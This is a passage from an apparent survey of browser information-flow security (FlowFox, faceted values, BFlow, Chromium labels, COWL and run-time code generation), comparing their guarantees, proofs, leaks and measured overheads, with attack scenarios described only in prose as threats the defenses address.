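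De Groef and colleagues concluded that FlowFox is compatible with the web of the time, meaning that it does not break sites that comply with the policy. The tests support this for the policy they used, a very mild one that treated only cookies as high. Under that policy, every call that changes the page is low, so everything in a FlowFox screenshot comes from the low run, which executes the original script with an empty cookie string. The crawl shows that the changes to the engine did not damage ordinary scripts, and that home pages look much the same when scripts cannot read cookies. Most of these pages probably had little use for cookies anyway, since the crawler was not logged in.

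The visits by logged-in users are better evidence because they involve real work on complicated sites. But the browser itself attaches the session cookie to each request, so a user can stay logged in even when scripts get an empty cookie string in the low run.

Pages are difficult when they must show the user something that a script computed from a secret. In a loan calculator, for example, if the visitor's income is labeled high, the call that displays the monthly payment must be high too, and so must any call that could read the payment back from the page. None of the recorded visits that De Groef and colleagues describe involves such a page. The test on *The Sun* came closest, but it consisted only of selecting text. It showed that the text stayed in the browser, but not whether a reader could still paste it with the added link.

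The screenshots also can't show whether a page sent different requests in the background, and the mask hid many advertisements, which often come from the third-party scripts that FlowFox is supposed to control.

### What the second run costs

De Groef and colleagues ran the V8 benchmark suite in FlowFox on a laptop with a 2 GHz dual-core processor. With two levels, execution time roughly doubled, as expected for programs that only compute. Programs that make heavy use of data structures slowed down even when FlowFox ran them only once, presumably because it also stores a level with each property.

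| What they measured | Result with two levels |
|---|---|
| Pure computation (V8 benchmarks) | roughly double the time |
| Test program that mostly waits for input and output | little change |
| Six recorded visits to real sites | about 20% more time |
| Memory, averaged over the 500 home pages | 88% more |

The program in the second row waits 10 milliseconds for each input or output. While one run waits, the other can continue, so the second run adds hardly any time. Real pages fall between these extremes, since they spend much of their time waiting for the network.

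De Groef and colleagues measured the 20% overhead over a whole visit, including network and display time, against unmodified Firefox. Bichhawat and colleagues measured only the time spent running JavaScript, without a JIT compiler, so their overheads cannot be compared directly with the 20%. The whole-visit figure is closer to what a user would notice, but it makes the mechanism's own overhead look smaller.

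Devriese and Piessens had found that secure multi-execution can be faster than normal execution. An ordinary JavaScript program waits for each input and output before it continues. If a script has one slow operation at each level, two parallel runs can do both at the same time. Parallel runs save time on a multi-core processor, but they all occupy memory at once. Running the levels one after another multiplies the time but needs little extra memory, because each run ends before the next begins.

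FlowFox runs the levels in turn, but this saves less memory than might be expected. A web page stays active after its scripts have loaded, and its event handlers may need their data at either level, so the browser has to keep both versions of the objects.

De Groef and colleagues compare FlowFox's overhead with that of early tools that checked C programs for memory errors. The first such tools compatible with existing code made programs ten times slower, and a decade of research reduced the overhead to 60%. The comparison is only partly convincing, because much of FlowFox's overhead comes from running everything twice, which tuning can't remove. De Groef and colleagues point to faceted values, which keep two versions only where a secret makes a difference, as a way to avoid much of the repetition.

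The cost also grows with the number of levels, because each level needs its own run. Two levels are enough to keep secrets on one site, but a page with several parties may need to record which of them each piece of data came from. JSFlow's labels are sets of origins, and every set that can occur would be a separate level:

| Origins on the page | Possible sets of origins | Runs in the worst case |
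|---|---|---|
| 1 | 2 | 2 |
| 3 | 8 | 8 |
| 10 | 1,024 | 1,024 |

Devriese and Piessens limit the number of runs somewhat by counting only levels at which the program has an input or output. A monitor with labels runs the script only once, however many labels there are. De Groef and colleagues wrote in 2012 that FlowFox could handle any number of levels, though with considerable overhead. The prototype had exactly two levels built into its code. De Groef later thought that processors with many cores might make a few more levels practical.

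### The proof of 2014 and what it assumes

The 2012 paper relied on the proof by Devriese and Piessens, whose model language has no events and no browser. De Groef, Devriese and colleagues (2014) added a formal model of FlowFox and proved noninterference for it. A script in the model consists of event handlers and calls to browser functions. Everything else, including the DOM, the user and the servers, is part of what they call the "world".

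Take a page with two handlers. One sends the cookie over the network when the page loads, and the other sends each key the user presses. Suppose that the cookie is 5, the user presses key 10, and the policy's default value for the cookie is 1. Reading the cookie and pressing a key are high, and loading the page and sending data are low. The model produces these steps:

| Step | Ordinary browser | FlowFox |
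|---|---|---|
| 1 | the page loads | the page loads |
| 2 | the script reads the cookie, 5 | the low run sends 1 |
| 3 | the script sends 5 | the high run reads the cookie, 5 |
| 4 | the user presses key 10 | the user presses key 10 |
| 5 | the script sends 10 | the high run skips the sending |

The theorem compares two executions of the same script in FlowFox, in worlds that may contain different secrets. For any public call in the first execution and any public call in the second, if both executions had received the same public inputs up to those points, the two calls use the same function with the same argument. The proof follows both executions step by step and shows that their low parts remain identical until they receive different public inputs.

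The theorem covers only leaks through scripts. If the browser itself passes a secret from a high call to a low one, FlowFox does not stop it. Suppose a policy makes writing a cookie high but reading a cookie low. The high run can write a secret into a cookie, and the low run can later read it and send it out. The guarantee is therefore meaningful only if the policy fits the browser. De Groef and colleagues define this fit as a second noninterference condition, which applies to the world. After receiving the same public calls, the world must respond to the next public call in the same way, whatever secrets it has received.

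Policies that make only some reading functions high meet this condition, because the high run then never changes anything in the browser. The policies in the experiments were of this type. More useful policies need more care. In the background-color example, the high run may set the page's color, so a malicious script could encode part of the cookie in it. If the function that reads the current color is still low, the low run can use it in a later event to recover that part of the cookie. The policy writer would have to know about every such pair among the many functions Firefox offers scripts. The same problem arises when a server sends secret data back to the page, or when an attacker tricks a user into retyping a secret.

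The proof of secure multi-execution also requires a deterministic language and a deterministic scheduler, so that the same inputs always lead to the same steps. FlowFox makes its scheduler deterministic by always completing the low run before the high one. JavaScript has a few sources of unpredictable behavior, but De Groef and colleagues considered them irrelevant in practice, apart from functions that a script schedules for later with `setTimeout`, which FlowFox treats as ordinary events.

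No proof covers the C++ code. JavaScript depends on the browser for all input and output, so a single check in XPConnect should catch every such call. This check is much less code to get right than JSFlow's library models, but a mistake elsewhere in Firefox could still undo the protection.

### Delays and changed order

The order of the runs has two side effects. The first is that it can change how harmless scripts behave. In the table above, the ordinary browser reads the cookie before it sends anything, while FlowFox reads it afterwards. An observer who can see only one level cannot detect this reordering. But the two runs share one browser, and a high call may depend on an earlier low one. De Groef imagines a high function that returns the number of bytes the browser has sent. If a harmless script displays this number and then sends some data, FlowFox sends the data first and displays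 a different number. FlowFox therefore does not fully inherit the precision that Devriese and Piessens proved, although the compatibility tests suggest that this rarely matters.

The second side effect is a timing leak. Devriese and Piessens closed the timing channel by requiring that a low run never wait for a high one. FlowFox meets this requirement within one event but not between events, because it completes the high handler before starting the next event. Suppose a page requests an image ten times a second, and its key handler loops for a second if the user presses "a". When the high run executes the loop, the image requests stop for a second, and the server can detect that the user pressed "a". Rafnsson and Sabelfeld, in *Secure Multi-Execution*, give an example of such an attack on FlowFox. A better scheduler would have to interrupt the high run in the middle of a handler, which browsers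 do not normally do.

### Repairs that the user does not notice

When a script tries to leak a secret, FlowFox repairs the run without stopping it or reporting the leak. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) gives a general reason for this approach. No method can detect exactly which programs violate noninterference, so a method that never raises a false alarm has to change programs instead of deciding whether they violate it. According to the paper, all known methods of this kind are forms of multi-execution. De Groef also defends the approach on the grounds that users dislike security warnings and tend to ignore them.

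A bad default value can then break the page. In the e-mail script of Devriese and Piessens, the low run receives `undefined` as the text of the message, which the script then searches with `text.indexOf('abc')`. In a real browser this call throws an exception, because `undefined` has no methods, and the low run would stop before it requested the image. An empty string would avoid the problem. De Groef encountered a few such crashes in the FlowFox experiments and had to adapt the policy. A crash in the low run is serious because that run draws the page under most policies.

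A default value that doesn't crash the script may do more harm than one that does. Suppose a policy makes a visitor's income high, with a default of 0, but leaves the call that displays a loan calculator's result low. The low run calculates with an income of 0 and displays a result that the visitor has no reason to doubt. JSFlow would stop the script or report the leak, which is annoying but gives someone a chance to correct the policy.

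FlowFox computes the information it would need to give a warning. In the cookie example, the high run builds an image address with the cookie in it, and the low run builds one without it. The difference shows that the script tried to leak something. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld developed a form of secure multi-execution that compares the public operations of the two runs, reports an attack when they differ, and preserves the original order of all outputs. It too would need a browser that can interrupt a script and resume it later.

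Some sites have a good reason to release part of a secret, such as the number of clicks but not their positions. FlowFox as published in 2012 and 2014 cannot do this, because the low run receives either the real input or the default. Vanhoef and colleagues later extended FlowFox with rules for such releases.

By 2016 De Groef did not expect browsers to adopt secure multi-execution because he thought it had too many problems. Users would have to install a modified version of Firefox, and someone would have to update the modifications for every new release. A website could also easily detect FlowFox and run slowly in it to make visitors switch back to their old browser, or use FlowFox's rarity to track them. He was still satisfied with the technique's influence on research.

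## ZaphodFacets: one run that keeps two versions of a value

With faceted values, the interpreter runs the script once and keeps two versions only of the values that depend on a secret, which avoids much of the repetition in secure multi-execution. Austin and Flanagan built the method into Firefox in a prototype called ZaphodFacets.

In the faceted value `⟨k ? 42 : 0⟩`, `k` is a principal, meaning a party with secrets. On a web page, a principal is roughly a domain. Observers who may see `k`'s secrets get the private part, 42, and everyone else gets the public part, 0.

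### A small program, step by step

The following program adds a calculation and an output to the three-line leak of Hedin and colleagues. The function `send` stands for any output.

```
x = makePrivate(42) || 0;
y = x + 1;
l = 1; t = 0;
if (y > 10) {t = 1;}
if (t != 1) {l = 0;}
send(l);
```

ZaphodFacets adds the function `makePrivate` to JavaScript. Calling `makePrivate(42)` returns `⟨k ? 42 : undefined⟩`, which has a private version, 42, and a public version, `undefined`. In `makePrivate(42) || 0`, the interpreter applies `|| 0`, a common JavaScript way to set a default, to both versions. The private version stays 42, and the public version becomes 0.

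| Line | What the interpreter does | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | creates the secret and its public default | x = ⟨k ? 42 : 0⟩ |
| 2 | adds 1 to both parts | y = ⟨k ? 43 : 1⟩ |
| 3 | stores two ordinary values | l = 1, t = 0 |
| 4 | runs the assignment for the private part only | t = ⟨k ? 1 : 0⟩ |
| 5 | runs the assignment for the public part only | l = ⟨k ? 1 : 0⟩ |
| 6 | picks the part that the receiver may see | 1 for k, 0 for anyone else |

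In line 4, the test evaluates to `⟨k ? true : false⟩`, so the interpreter must follow both outcomes. It first takes `true`, with `k` in the pc, and writes change only the private part of a variable. It then takes `false`, with "not k" in the pc, and writes change only the public part. There is no `else`, so the second pass executes nothing. After the conditional, the interpreter continues with a single run.

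If the secret were 5 instead of 42, both parts of `y` would fail the test in line 4. Then `t` would stay 0 and `l` would become 0 for everyone. Public receivers get 0 with either secret.

### Why the program does not have to stop

The no-sensitive-upgrade rule would stop this program at `t = 1`. The permissive-upgrade variant would stop it at line 5, which needs the public value of `t` that line 4 overwrote. Faceted evaluation keeps that value, 0, so it can continue.

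Austin and Flanagan proved that every program that finishes under either of the older rules also finishes with facets and gives the same result. The proof covers a small model language with one principal and no input or output.

The main theorem, the projection theorem, covers several principals as well as input and output. It says that replacing every faceted value in a run that finishes with the part a given observer may see yields an ordinary run of the program on the inputs that observer may see. Noninterference follows almost immediately, because if two faceted runs differ only in their secrets, a public observer's view of both is the same ordinary run, so the public results must agree. The argument requires a deterministic language and covers only runs that finish.

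Faceted values can also contain each other. Suppose `a` and `b` are two principals and a script adds `⟨a ? 2 : 0⟩` and `⟨b ? 1 : 0⟩`. The result is `⟨a ? ⟨b ? 3 : 2⟩ : ⟨b ? 1 : 0⟩⟩`, which has a version for each kind of observer:

| Whose secrets the observer may see | Sum |
|---|---|
| both | 3 |
| only a's | 2 |
| only b's | 1 |
| neither | 0 |

With n principals, one faceted run can therefore simulate 2ⁿ ordinary runs, and a single value may need up to 2ⁿ versions.

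### Releasing part of a secret

Some programs have to reveal something about a secret, such as whether a password was correct. Under secure multi-execution, the secret run must pass this answer to the public run, which requires careful coordination. With facets, a single value holds both versions, so the interpreter can copy the private version into the public one.

An attacker could try to make legitimate code release the password itself. To prevent this, Austin and Flanagan add a second kind of label to their formal model, for data that a principal does not trust. A program may release a secret only if no untrusted data influenced the decision, and the release makes only the trusted version of the secret public.

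### What the Firefox prototype covered

ZaphodFacets combines three existing pieces of software. Narcissus is a JavaScript engine written in JavaScript, and Zaphod is the Firefox add-on that uses Narcissus to run a page's scripts. Snowfox, the JSFlow extension, also reuses Zaphod. The third, dom.js, implements the DOM in JavaScript, which lets ZaphodFacets keep both versions of a value when a script stores it in the page.

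Austin and Flanagan demonstrate this with an attack on a page that hashes passwords in the browser. The attacker's script replaces the hashing function with one that writes the password into an attribute of a heading. It then finds the heading by another route, reads the password back, and puts it into the address of an image on evil.com. ZaphodFacets keeps the password as a faceted value when it passes through the DOM, whereas a system that lost track of values there would treat it as public. The policy gives other origins only the public part, so evil.com doesn't receive the password. The site's own server gets the real value, so the user can still log in.

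The prototype halts a script if an exception might leak information, so some of the unnecessary stops remain. *Multiple Facets for Dynamic Information Flow with Exceptions* (Austin, Schmitz and Flanagan, 2017) later extended the method to exceptions. The screen can show only one version of each value, even though the DOM stores both. The example policy protects only password fields, and Austin and Flanagan call it far from complete. They report one attack and one benchmark but no tests on live websites, whereas FlowFox was tested on 500 home pages.

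### The benchmark

To compare facets with secure multi-execution, Austin and Flanagan built both into Narcissus. They used crypto-md5, a hashing program from the SunSpider suite, and changed it to compute eight hashes. In the test with one principal, one of the eight inputs was secret. With eight principals, all eight were secret, each belonging to a different principal. The computer was a MacBook Pro with a four-core 2.3 GHz processor. These are the times in seconds:

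| Principals | Multi-execution, runs in sequence | Multi-execution, runs in parallel | Facets |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 273.8 | 283.5 | 310.6 |
| 1 | 513.6 | 283.5 | 348.7 |
| 2 | 961.4 | 332.3 | 387.1 |
| 3 | 1,783.6 | 597.6 | 421.6 |
| 4 | 3,324.5 | 1,094.0 | 461.5 |
| 5 | over an hour | 1,981.9 | 503.4 |
| 6 | over an hour | over an hour | 540.6 |
| 7 | over an hour | over an hour | 575.1 |
| 8 | over an hour | over an hour | 614.2 |

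Without secrets, facets were about 13% slower than sequential multi-execution, which then runs the script only once, because the interpreter has to check for faceted values even when there are none. With one or more principals, facets were faster than sequential multi-execution. Parallel multi-execution was faster than facets with up to two principals, which require four runs, one for each core. With three or more principals, which require at least eight runs, facets were faster.

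The facet times rise by about 38 seconds per principal, or an eighth of the time the test takes without secrets. This fits the test's design, because each new secret makes the interpreter compute one of the eight hashes twice. With eight principals it computes 16 hashes, whereas multi-execution would need 256 runs of eight hashes each, or 2,048 hashes in total.

The test suits facets very well, because it hashes each secret separately. If a script combined all eight secrets in one value, that value could have up to 256 versions, and every later calculation with it could take 256 times as long. The figures also don't show how much facets would slow down an ordinary browser. Even without secrets, the program took more than four and a half minutes, probably because Narcissus runs in JavaScript.

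### Combining facets with separate runs

Facets save work by keeping the secret and public computations in one run, but this also lets one block the other. *Faceted Secure Multi Execution* (Schmitz, Algehed and colleagues, 2018) gives an example program that reads a secret, loops forever if it is 42, and then writes 0 to a public file. With facets, the interpreter never gets past the loop if the secret is 42, so anyone who can read the public file learns the secret from the missing 0. Secure multi-execution can prevent this if it runs the levels in parallel, because the public run doesn't wait for the secret one.

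The hybrid starts with facets. If a computation that depends on a secret seems to take too long, the system splits into two parallel executions, one for observers who may see the secret and one for everyone else. In the example, the second execution writes the 0 while the first is still looping. Both executions keep using facets, so they split again only if another computation takes too long. An earlier hybrid by Ngo and colleagues restarted the program with one thread for every level, which lost all the efficiency gains from facets and required a complete list of levels in advance.

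Schmitz and colleagues checked their security proofs in Coq, assuming that the scheduler gives every execution its turn. They built the system as a Haskell library and used it for a file-hosting service, so their results do not show how the hybrid would perform in a browser.

The hybrid lets a developer trade memory for time, because facets store many versions of a value while separate runs repeat the computation. But the use of either resource can grow exponentially with the number of principals whose data a program combines. *Optimising Faceted Secure Multi-Execution* (Algehed, Russo and Flanagan, 2019) reduces this growth in two ways.

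The first is to simplify faceted values without changing what anyone sees. Multiplying `⟨Alice ? 1 : 0⟩` by `⟨Bob ? 1 : 0⟩` gives a value with four versions, but three of them are 0. Only an observer who may see both secrets gets 1, so the system can replace the value with `⟨{Alice, Bob} ? 1 : 0⟩`, which has two versions.

The second is to avoid computing versions that nobody will use. If part of a program writes only to Bob's file, it doesn't need the versions for observers who may see Alice's secrets. The programmer has to supply this information in an annotation. A wrong annotation cannot leak a secret, but it can change the results of a harmless program.

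In two case studies, a database and a chat server, these methods significantly reduced the overhead, in some cases from exponential to polynomial. Algehed and colleagues used the proof assistant Agda to prove the methods correct for a core language without memory updates, input or output, and they argue that the methods extend to these features.

### The price of preserving every secure program

Facets and secure multi-execution are both attempts at transparent enforcement, which guarantees security without changing the behavior of any program that is already secure. In *Transparent IFC Enforcement*, Algehed and Flanagan examine how much overhead any such method must have. They use a model simpler than a web page, in which a program receives all its input at the start, each piece labeled, and either produces its output or runs forever.

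Even in this model, ordinary multi-execution does not preserve the behavior of every secure program. Suppose a program finishes only if a certain secret is present, but its output reveals nothing about that secret. The public run doesn't have the secret, so it never finishes. Algehed and Flanagan solve this with a method that tries many possible inputs in parallel until the program finishes on one of them. Their method answers an open question by showing that full transparency is possible for termination-insensitive noninterference, but it is far too slow to use.

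The first result on running time is that every transparent method is closely related to multi-execution. Given any transparent method that is fast on secure programs, one could apply it to a program, note which labels appear on the output, and then run the original program once for each of those labels. This procedure is a form of multi-execution, and it takes at most polynomially longer than the method it started with. Any limit on the speed of multi-execution therefore applies to all transparent methods. The result covers secure programs that run in polynomial time and still finish when the system removes their secret inputs.

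The second result is that no black-box method can be both transparent and efficient if the number of principals is unlimited and the method doesn't know all the labels in advance. A black-box method can run a program on inputs of its choice but cannot examine its code. "Efficient" here means that the method's running time grows only polynomially for secure programs that are fast and always finish.

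The proof relies on the number of possible groups of principals, which doubles with each new principal. An efficient method can make only polynomially many test runs, so with enough principals it must leave some group G untested. The proof then uses a program that outputs 1, labeled for G, if its input comes from exactly the members of G, and otherwise outputs nothing.

| Who supplies input | What the method finds in its tests | What it must output |
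|---|---|---|
| all principals | the program never outputs anything | nothing |
| only the members of G | the program outputs 1 when all of G supply input | 1 |

In both rows, the program looks exactly like a secure one, so a transparent method must not change its output. An observer who may see only G's data can then tell the two rows apart and learn whether anyone outside G supplied input, so the method has allowed a leak.

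This proof does not apply to facets, which are not a black-box method because the interpreter follows the program's code. Algehed and Flanagan conjecture that examining the code cannot make transparent enforcement efficient in general either. They leave programs that respond to events for later work, but see no reason to expect these to be easier to secure.

The exponential overhead comes from the number of ways labels can combine, as *Multi-Execution Lattices Fast and Slow* (Algehed and Flanagan, 2021) also points out. If each level includes the one below it, ten levels need only ten runs, so a browser with two levels, such as FlowFox, can still be practical. The results also do not rule out methods that are fast on typical programs and slow only on unusual ones.

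## Labels on whole pages and frames: BFlow, Chromium and COWL

A browser can also put a single label on a whole script, frame or page. Once a script in a frame has read a secret, the browser treats everything that frame later sends as secret. It then has to check only what crosses the frame's boundary, so the JavaScript engine doesn't need to change.

### A harmless request that the browser blocks

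Suppose a script on a private blog reads the posts and then loads a background picture from a photo site. The function `readPosts` stands for any read of private data.

```
posts = readPosts();
img = new Image();
img.src = "http://photos.example/sky.jpg";
```

The address is fixed text, so the request reveals nothing about the posts.

| Step | Labels on values | One label on the frame |
|---|---|---|
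| Read the posts | `posts` becomes secret | the whole frame becomes secret |
| Write the address | the address is public | the address is secret, like everything in the frame |
| Request the picture | allowed | blocked |

With a frame label, the browser cannot distinguish this request from one with the posts in its address. If the script loaded the picture before reading the posts, both methods would allow it. If a loan calculator's script had already read the visitor's income, a frame label would also block the harmless Google Analytics reports that JSFlow allowed.

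Yip, Narula and colleagues encountered the problem with a real extension for Blogger, Google's blog service (*Privacy-Preserving Browser-Side Scripting With BFlow*, 2009). The extension read a blog's newest posts and then tried to load a JavaScript file from another site. Their system, BFlow, blocked the load, so they copied the file into the extension.

Reordering doesn't help if the private posts are already in the page's HTML. In that case, BFlow lets the site's developer list specific files from other sites in advance. The blog's server fetches them and passes them to the browser, so the photo site never receives a request that a secret could have influenced.

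### BFlow

BFlow consists of a Firefox add-on and software on the web server. It groups frames into protection zones, each with one label. Frames in the same zone can read each other's variables, which suits programs such as a chat tool with one frame for messages and another for typing.

A label is a set of tags that the server defines, such as a tag for Alice's private blog. Data may pass from one zone to another only if the receiving zone's label contains all the sender's tags. A zone with a tag may contact only the server that issued the tag, unless the site has made an exception.

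The browser attaches the zone's label to each request to that server, and the server must store the label with any data it saves. This protects against scripts that leak a secret by publishing it on the site's own pages, as in Hedin and Sabelfeld's forum attack.

Yip and colleagues adapted twelve existing scripts to BFlow. Seven handled no confidential data and ran unchanged. The other five handled confidential data and needed changes, with one or two lines changed in four of them and 89 lines in a chat program. For two of the five, the site also had to let an outside service read the blog's confidential comments. Two malicious extensions that the group wrote could steal data from the real Blogger but not from a version running under BFlow. The group expected little slowdown but did not measure it.

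### Labels throughout Chromium

BFlow tracks data in frames and in requests to servers, but a malicious browser extension could switch it off. In *Run-time Monitoring and Formal Analysis of Information Flows in Chromium* (2015), Bauer, Cai and colleagues extended labels to most of Chromium, including its extensions. Chromium is the open-source browser behind Google Chrome.

Their labels have three parts, which list the secrets that something may contain, the sensitive browser functions it may use, and its rights to make exceptions, such as removing a tag. Some labels rise automatically when new secrets arrive, up to a fixed ceiling.

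| Part of the browser | Where its label comes from |
|---|---|
| Page | its Content Security Policy |
| Page element | its page, plus the secrets that scripts write into it |
| Extension | its permissions, which the user approves |
| Event, such as a click | the element involved and whoever caused the event |
| Cookie | the cookie's domain |
| History entry | whatever caused the entry |

Bauer and colleagues illustrate the system with a password manager and a malicious extension that claims to translate pages:

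1. The user types a password into the login form on cnn.com.
2. Both extensions read the form, and their labels rise to include cnn.com's user data.
3. The malicious extension tries to send the password to evil.com. The browser blocks the request, because the extension has no right to remove the cnn.com tag.
4. On a later visit, the password manager fills in the saved password, and the form field receives the manager's tag. This tag is above the malicious extension's ceiling, so the extension can't read the field at all.

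Bookmarks need different treatment because they are long-lived. If a script with many secrets changed the top of the bookmark tree, the labels could rise and make every bookmark unreadable to other scripts. The design therefore keeps a separate copy of the bookmarks for each secrecy level in use, an idea taken from secure multi-execution, but the prototype did not yet include this.

Some extensions can make the browser wait while they decide what to do with a web request. Suppose an extension knows a secret bit and redirects a request for cnn.com only if the bit is 0. Anyone who can observe whether cnn.com loads then learns the bit. The design therefore lets an extension handle such a blocking event only if the event and the handler have the same secrecy label.

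### A proof that depends on the scheduler

Bauer and colleagues proved a form of noninterference for a model of the browser. If two starting states differ only in secrets the attacker is not allowed to see, any sequence of actions the attacker could observe from one state is also possible from the other, as long as nothing uses a right to declassify.

This is weaker than it sounds, because the other sequence only has to be possible. In an example from the paper, `x`, `y` and `z` are page elements. `z` holds a secret, while `x` and `y` start out false and public. Two event handlers run one after the other:

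```
function first() {if (!z) {y = true;}}
function second() {if (!y) {x = true;}}
```

If `z` is true, the first handler writes nothing and the second sets `x` to true. If `z` is false, the first handler makes `y` secret. The second handler is not allowed to read secrets, so its attempt to read `y` never returns, and `x` stays false. Either way, `x` ends up equal to `z`, just as in the three-line program that leaks through a branch that does not run.

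The theorem permits this because the model doesn't fix when each handler runs. If `x` is true, the second handler might have run first. If `x` is false, it might not have run yet. Bauer and colleagues acknowledge that real browsers are predictable enough for an attacker to rule out these alternatives. They suggest making the order of events less predictable or using secure multi-execution.

### The cost of the Chromium prototype

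Page loads took 55% longer on average. Among the ten most popular websites, they ranged from 14% faster on Baidu to 103% slower on Wikipedia. Baidu's speedup is probably noise, since many sites served different content from one run to the next. Loading Google's home page required 29 label checks, and the Chinese portal QQ required 2,639. Bauer and colleagues had not optimized the prototype and expected that a better version could be very efficient.

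Compatibility was a bigger problem. Most pages without a Content Security Policy failed to load fully because their default label blocked them from fetching anything from other sites, so the group had to write policies by hand for the 100 most popular websites.

These policies also weaken the protection. Because any request can carry data, a page that loads advertisements needs permission to send its data to the advertising server. In the cnn.com example, this permission covers everything with a cnn.com tag.

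### COWL: confinement for pages that ask for it

*Toward Principled Browser Security* (Yang, Stefan and colleagues, 2013) treated the same-origin policy itself as a strict information-flow policy. The same group took a more cautious approach in *Protecting Users by Confining JavaScript with COWL* (Stefan, Yang and colleagues, 2014). COWL (Confinement with Origin Web Labels) leaves the browser's existing rules in place and adds its own only on pages that call its functions.

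COWL labels a context, meaning a page, a frame or a worker (a script that runs apart from the page). The label is a logical formula over origins. Data labeled "amazon.com or chase.com" may go to either company, whereas data labeled "amazon.com and chase.com" is sensitive to both, so neither may receive it alone. A script can give its own context such a label:

```
COWL.enable();
COWL.label = Label("https://amazon.com")
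  .and("https://chase.com");
```

From then on, the context cannot contact any server. A budgeting page could use this to compare a user's purchases with her bank statement. It would request both sets of data first, raise its label to read them, and then show her the result.

A page from a given origin also holds that origin's privilege, which lets it remove the origin from labels. Stefan and colleagues show how this works with a password-strength checker that the site does not trust:

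1. The page starts the checker in its own context with a public label, and the checker downloads its latest rules from its author's server.
2. The page sends the password as a "labeled Blob", a message with a label attached. The checker can hold the message without opening it and still use the network.
3. The checker raises its label to open the message, and the browser restricts its network access at the same moment.
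4. The checker sends back its verdict, labeled as secret. The page uses its privilege to read the verdict without becoming confined itself.

If the password had the site's ordinary label, the checker could still send it to the site's own server and perhaps publish it there. The page can prevent this by labeling the password with a new origin that matches no server.

Some libraries, such as jQuery, need access to the whole page, so a site can't put them in a separate context. With COWL, the site instead moves its trusted code into a worker, gives the worker the site's privileges, and confines the page that contains the library. The library can change anything on the page, but only the trusted worker can reach the network.

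### What COWL adds to the running time

Stefan and colleagues built COWL into Firefox and Chromium without changing either browser's JavaScript engine. Pages that did not use COWL ran at most 4% slower on Dromaeo, the DOM benchmark. For four small applications in Firefox, the group compared COWL with versions that had the same division into contexts but no security checks:

| Application | Without checks | With COWL |
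|---|---|---|
| Password checker | 22 ms | 18 ms |
| Encrypted document editor | 100 ms | 116 ms |
| Page combining data from two sites | 35 ms | 41 ms |
| Bank page with jQuery | 160 ms | 165 ms |

The password checker was faster because COWL's workers start more quickly than ordinary ones, but it was still about 5 ms slower than an unprotected script tag. The server ran on the same computer as the browser, so no network delay hid the overhead. The group wrote all four applications for COWL, so the figures do not include the work of dividing up an existing site.

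COWL does not stop covert channels, which carry information by means not intended for communication. For example, a confined script could vary how long the page takes to draw, and a script in another context could measure the delay and send out the result.

### From prototype to W3C draft

The team planned to make COWL a web standard. R&D World reported that they expected this to take about a year, with a first public draft by January. In September 2015, Hill (2015) asked W3C's Web Application Security Working Group to agree to publish a first draft, and W3C published *Confinement with Origin Web Labels* (2015) on 15 October. W3C said it intended the document to become a Recommendation, its term for a finished standard. In July 2026, that first draft was still the latest version in W3C's index.

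The draft is about sharing data with code that is "buggy but not malicious", a milder threat than the gadget attacker FlowFox was built to stop. In a later editor's draft, W3C changed the description from confining code to confining iframes.

Overhead in the JavaScript engine is probably not why browsers did not ship COWL. Stefan (2014) said in a talk that browser makers would reject a change that added even one instruction to the engine's most frequently used code, and the team designed COWL to avoid such changes. However, COWL requires site developers to divide their pages into contexts, so shipping it would have protected few users until many sites had done this work.

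### Generated code and lost precision

BFlow and COWL need no special rule for code generated at run time, because the browser never examines individual statements. Code passed to `eval` runs in the frame or worker that built it, under the same label, and anything it sends has to pass the same checks.

For the same reason, these systems do not need a pc label inside a frame. A branch on a secret can change only data that the browser already treats as secret. The leak in the Chromium prototype arises because the browser labels elements of one page separately and raises an element's label automatically when a script writes to it. In BFlow and COWL, the receiving context has to raise its own label before it can read a message's contents, and the message cannot raise that label.

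Because a label covers a whole frame, secret data also makes unrelated data in the same frame secret. Yip and colleagues give the example of a page where a user can edit a private phone number and a public profile. If both were in one frame, the profile would get the phone number's label and the site could no longer show the profile to the public, so the developer has to put them in separate frames.

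Stefan and colleagues conjecture that labels on contexts can express the same policies as labels on values if a developer can use as many contexts as needed. For older scripts that haven't been divided into separate contexts, they suggest running JSFlow inside a COWL context. That would restore the precision of labels on values within the context, but it would also bring JSFlow's slowdown.

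## Code generated at run time, and monitors written into the script

A label on a whole frame covers any code its scripts generate at run time. Systems that track individual values need a rule for such code, because it did not exist when they first examined the page.

### How pages create code, and how often

JavaScript and the browser offer several ways to turn text into running code:

- `eval(s)` runs the string `s` at once. The new code can read and change the local variables around the call. If the script calls `eval` through another name, the code can reach only global variables.
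- `new Function("x", s)` creates a function whose body is the string `s`.
- `setTimeout(s, 1000)` runs the string after a second, and `setInterval` runs it repeatedly.
- A script can insert a new script element into the page, containing either the code itself or the address of a file.
- `document.write` adds text to the page while the page is loading, and this text may include a script element.
- A handler attribute such as `onclick` holds code as text, which the browser runs when the event occurs.

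The largest count of these methods dates from 2011, when Richards, Hammer and colleagues, in *The Eval that Men Do*, recorded 550,358 calls to `eval` in a modified version of WebKit. They used the 100 most popular websites by hand for one to five minutes each, logging in where they could. A program also loaded the 10,000 most popular sites, once without any interaction and once with random clicks. These are the shares of sites that used each method at least once:

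| Method | Top 100 sites, used by hand | 10,000 sites, visited automatically |
|---|---|---|
| `eval` called directly | 83% | 23–31% |
| `eval` under another name | 10% | 1.3–1.6% |
| `Function` constructor | 49% | 8.8–13% |
| `setTimeout` with a string | 39% | 13–18% |
| Changed text of a script element | 67% | 23–32% |
| Changed address of a script element | 64% | 10–15% |
| `document.write` | 64% | 32–40% |

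About half as many sites used `setInterval` as `setTimeout`. The list of methods counted omits handler attributes. The figures for `eval` on the 10,000 sites are also uncertain, because the paper gives 50% and 52% elsewhere.

A monitor that controlled only `eval` would miss most generated code. In the manual sessions, fewer sites used the `Function` constructor than `eval`, but those sites called it more often than any other method in the table.

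Much of the code passed to `eval` did very little. Between 22% and 37% of the strings contained data in JSON, a text format based on JavaScript's own notation, or in a close variant that assigns the data to a variable or passes it to a function. Others looked up a variable whose name the script had put together, as on the German news site heute.de:

```
if (eval("flash" + i + "Installed") == true)
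  actualVersion = i;
```

The script already had the version number of the Flash plug-in. It used the number to set ten variables, `flash2Installed` through `flash11Installed`, and then looped through them to recover it.

Richards and colleagues judged that ordinary language features could replace the `eval` calls for about 76% of the strings from the manual sessions. In 2012, *Eval begone!* presented the Evalorizer, a tool that helps programmers make these replacements, and tested it on a real website. Calls that use local variables are harder to replace, because a script can look up a global variable by name as a property of `window`, but JavaScript has no such notation for local variables. About 41% of the strings from the manual sessions used local variables without reading or changing global ones.

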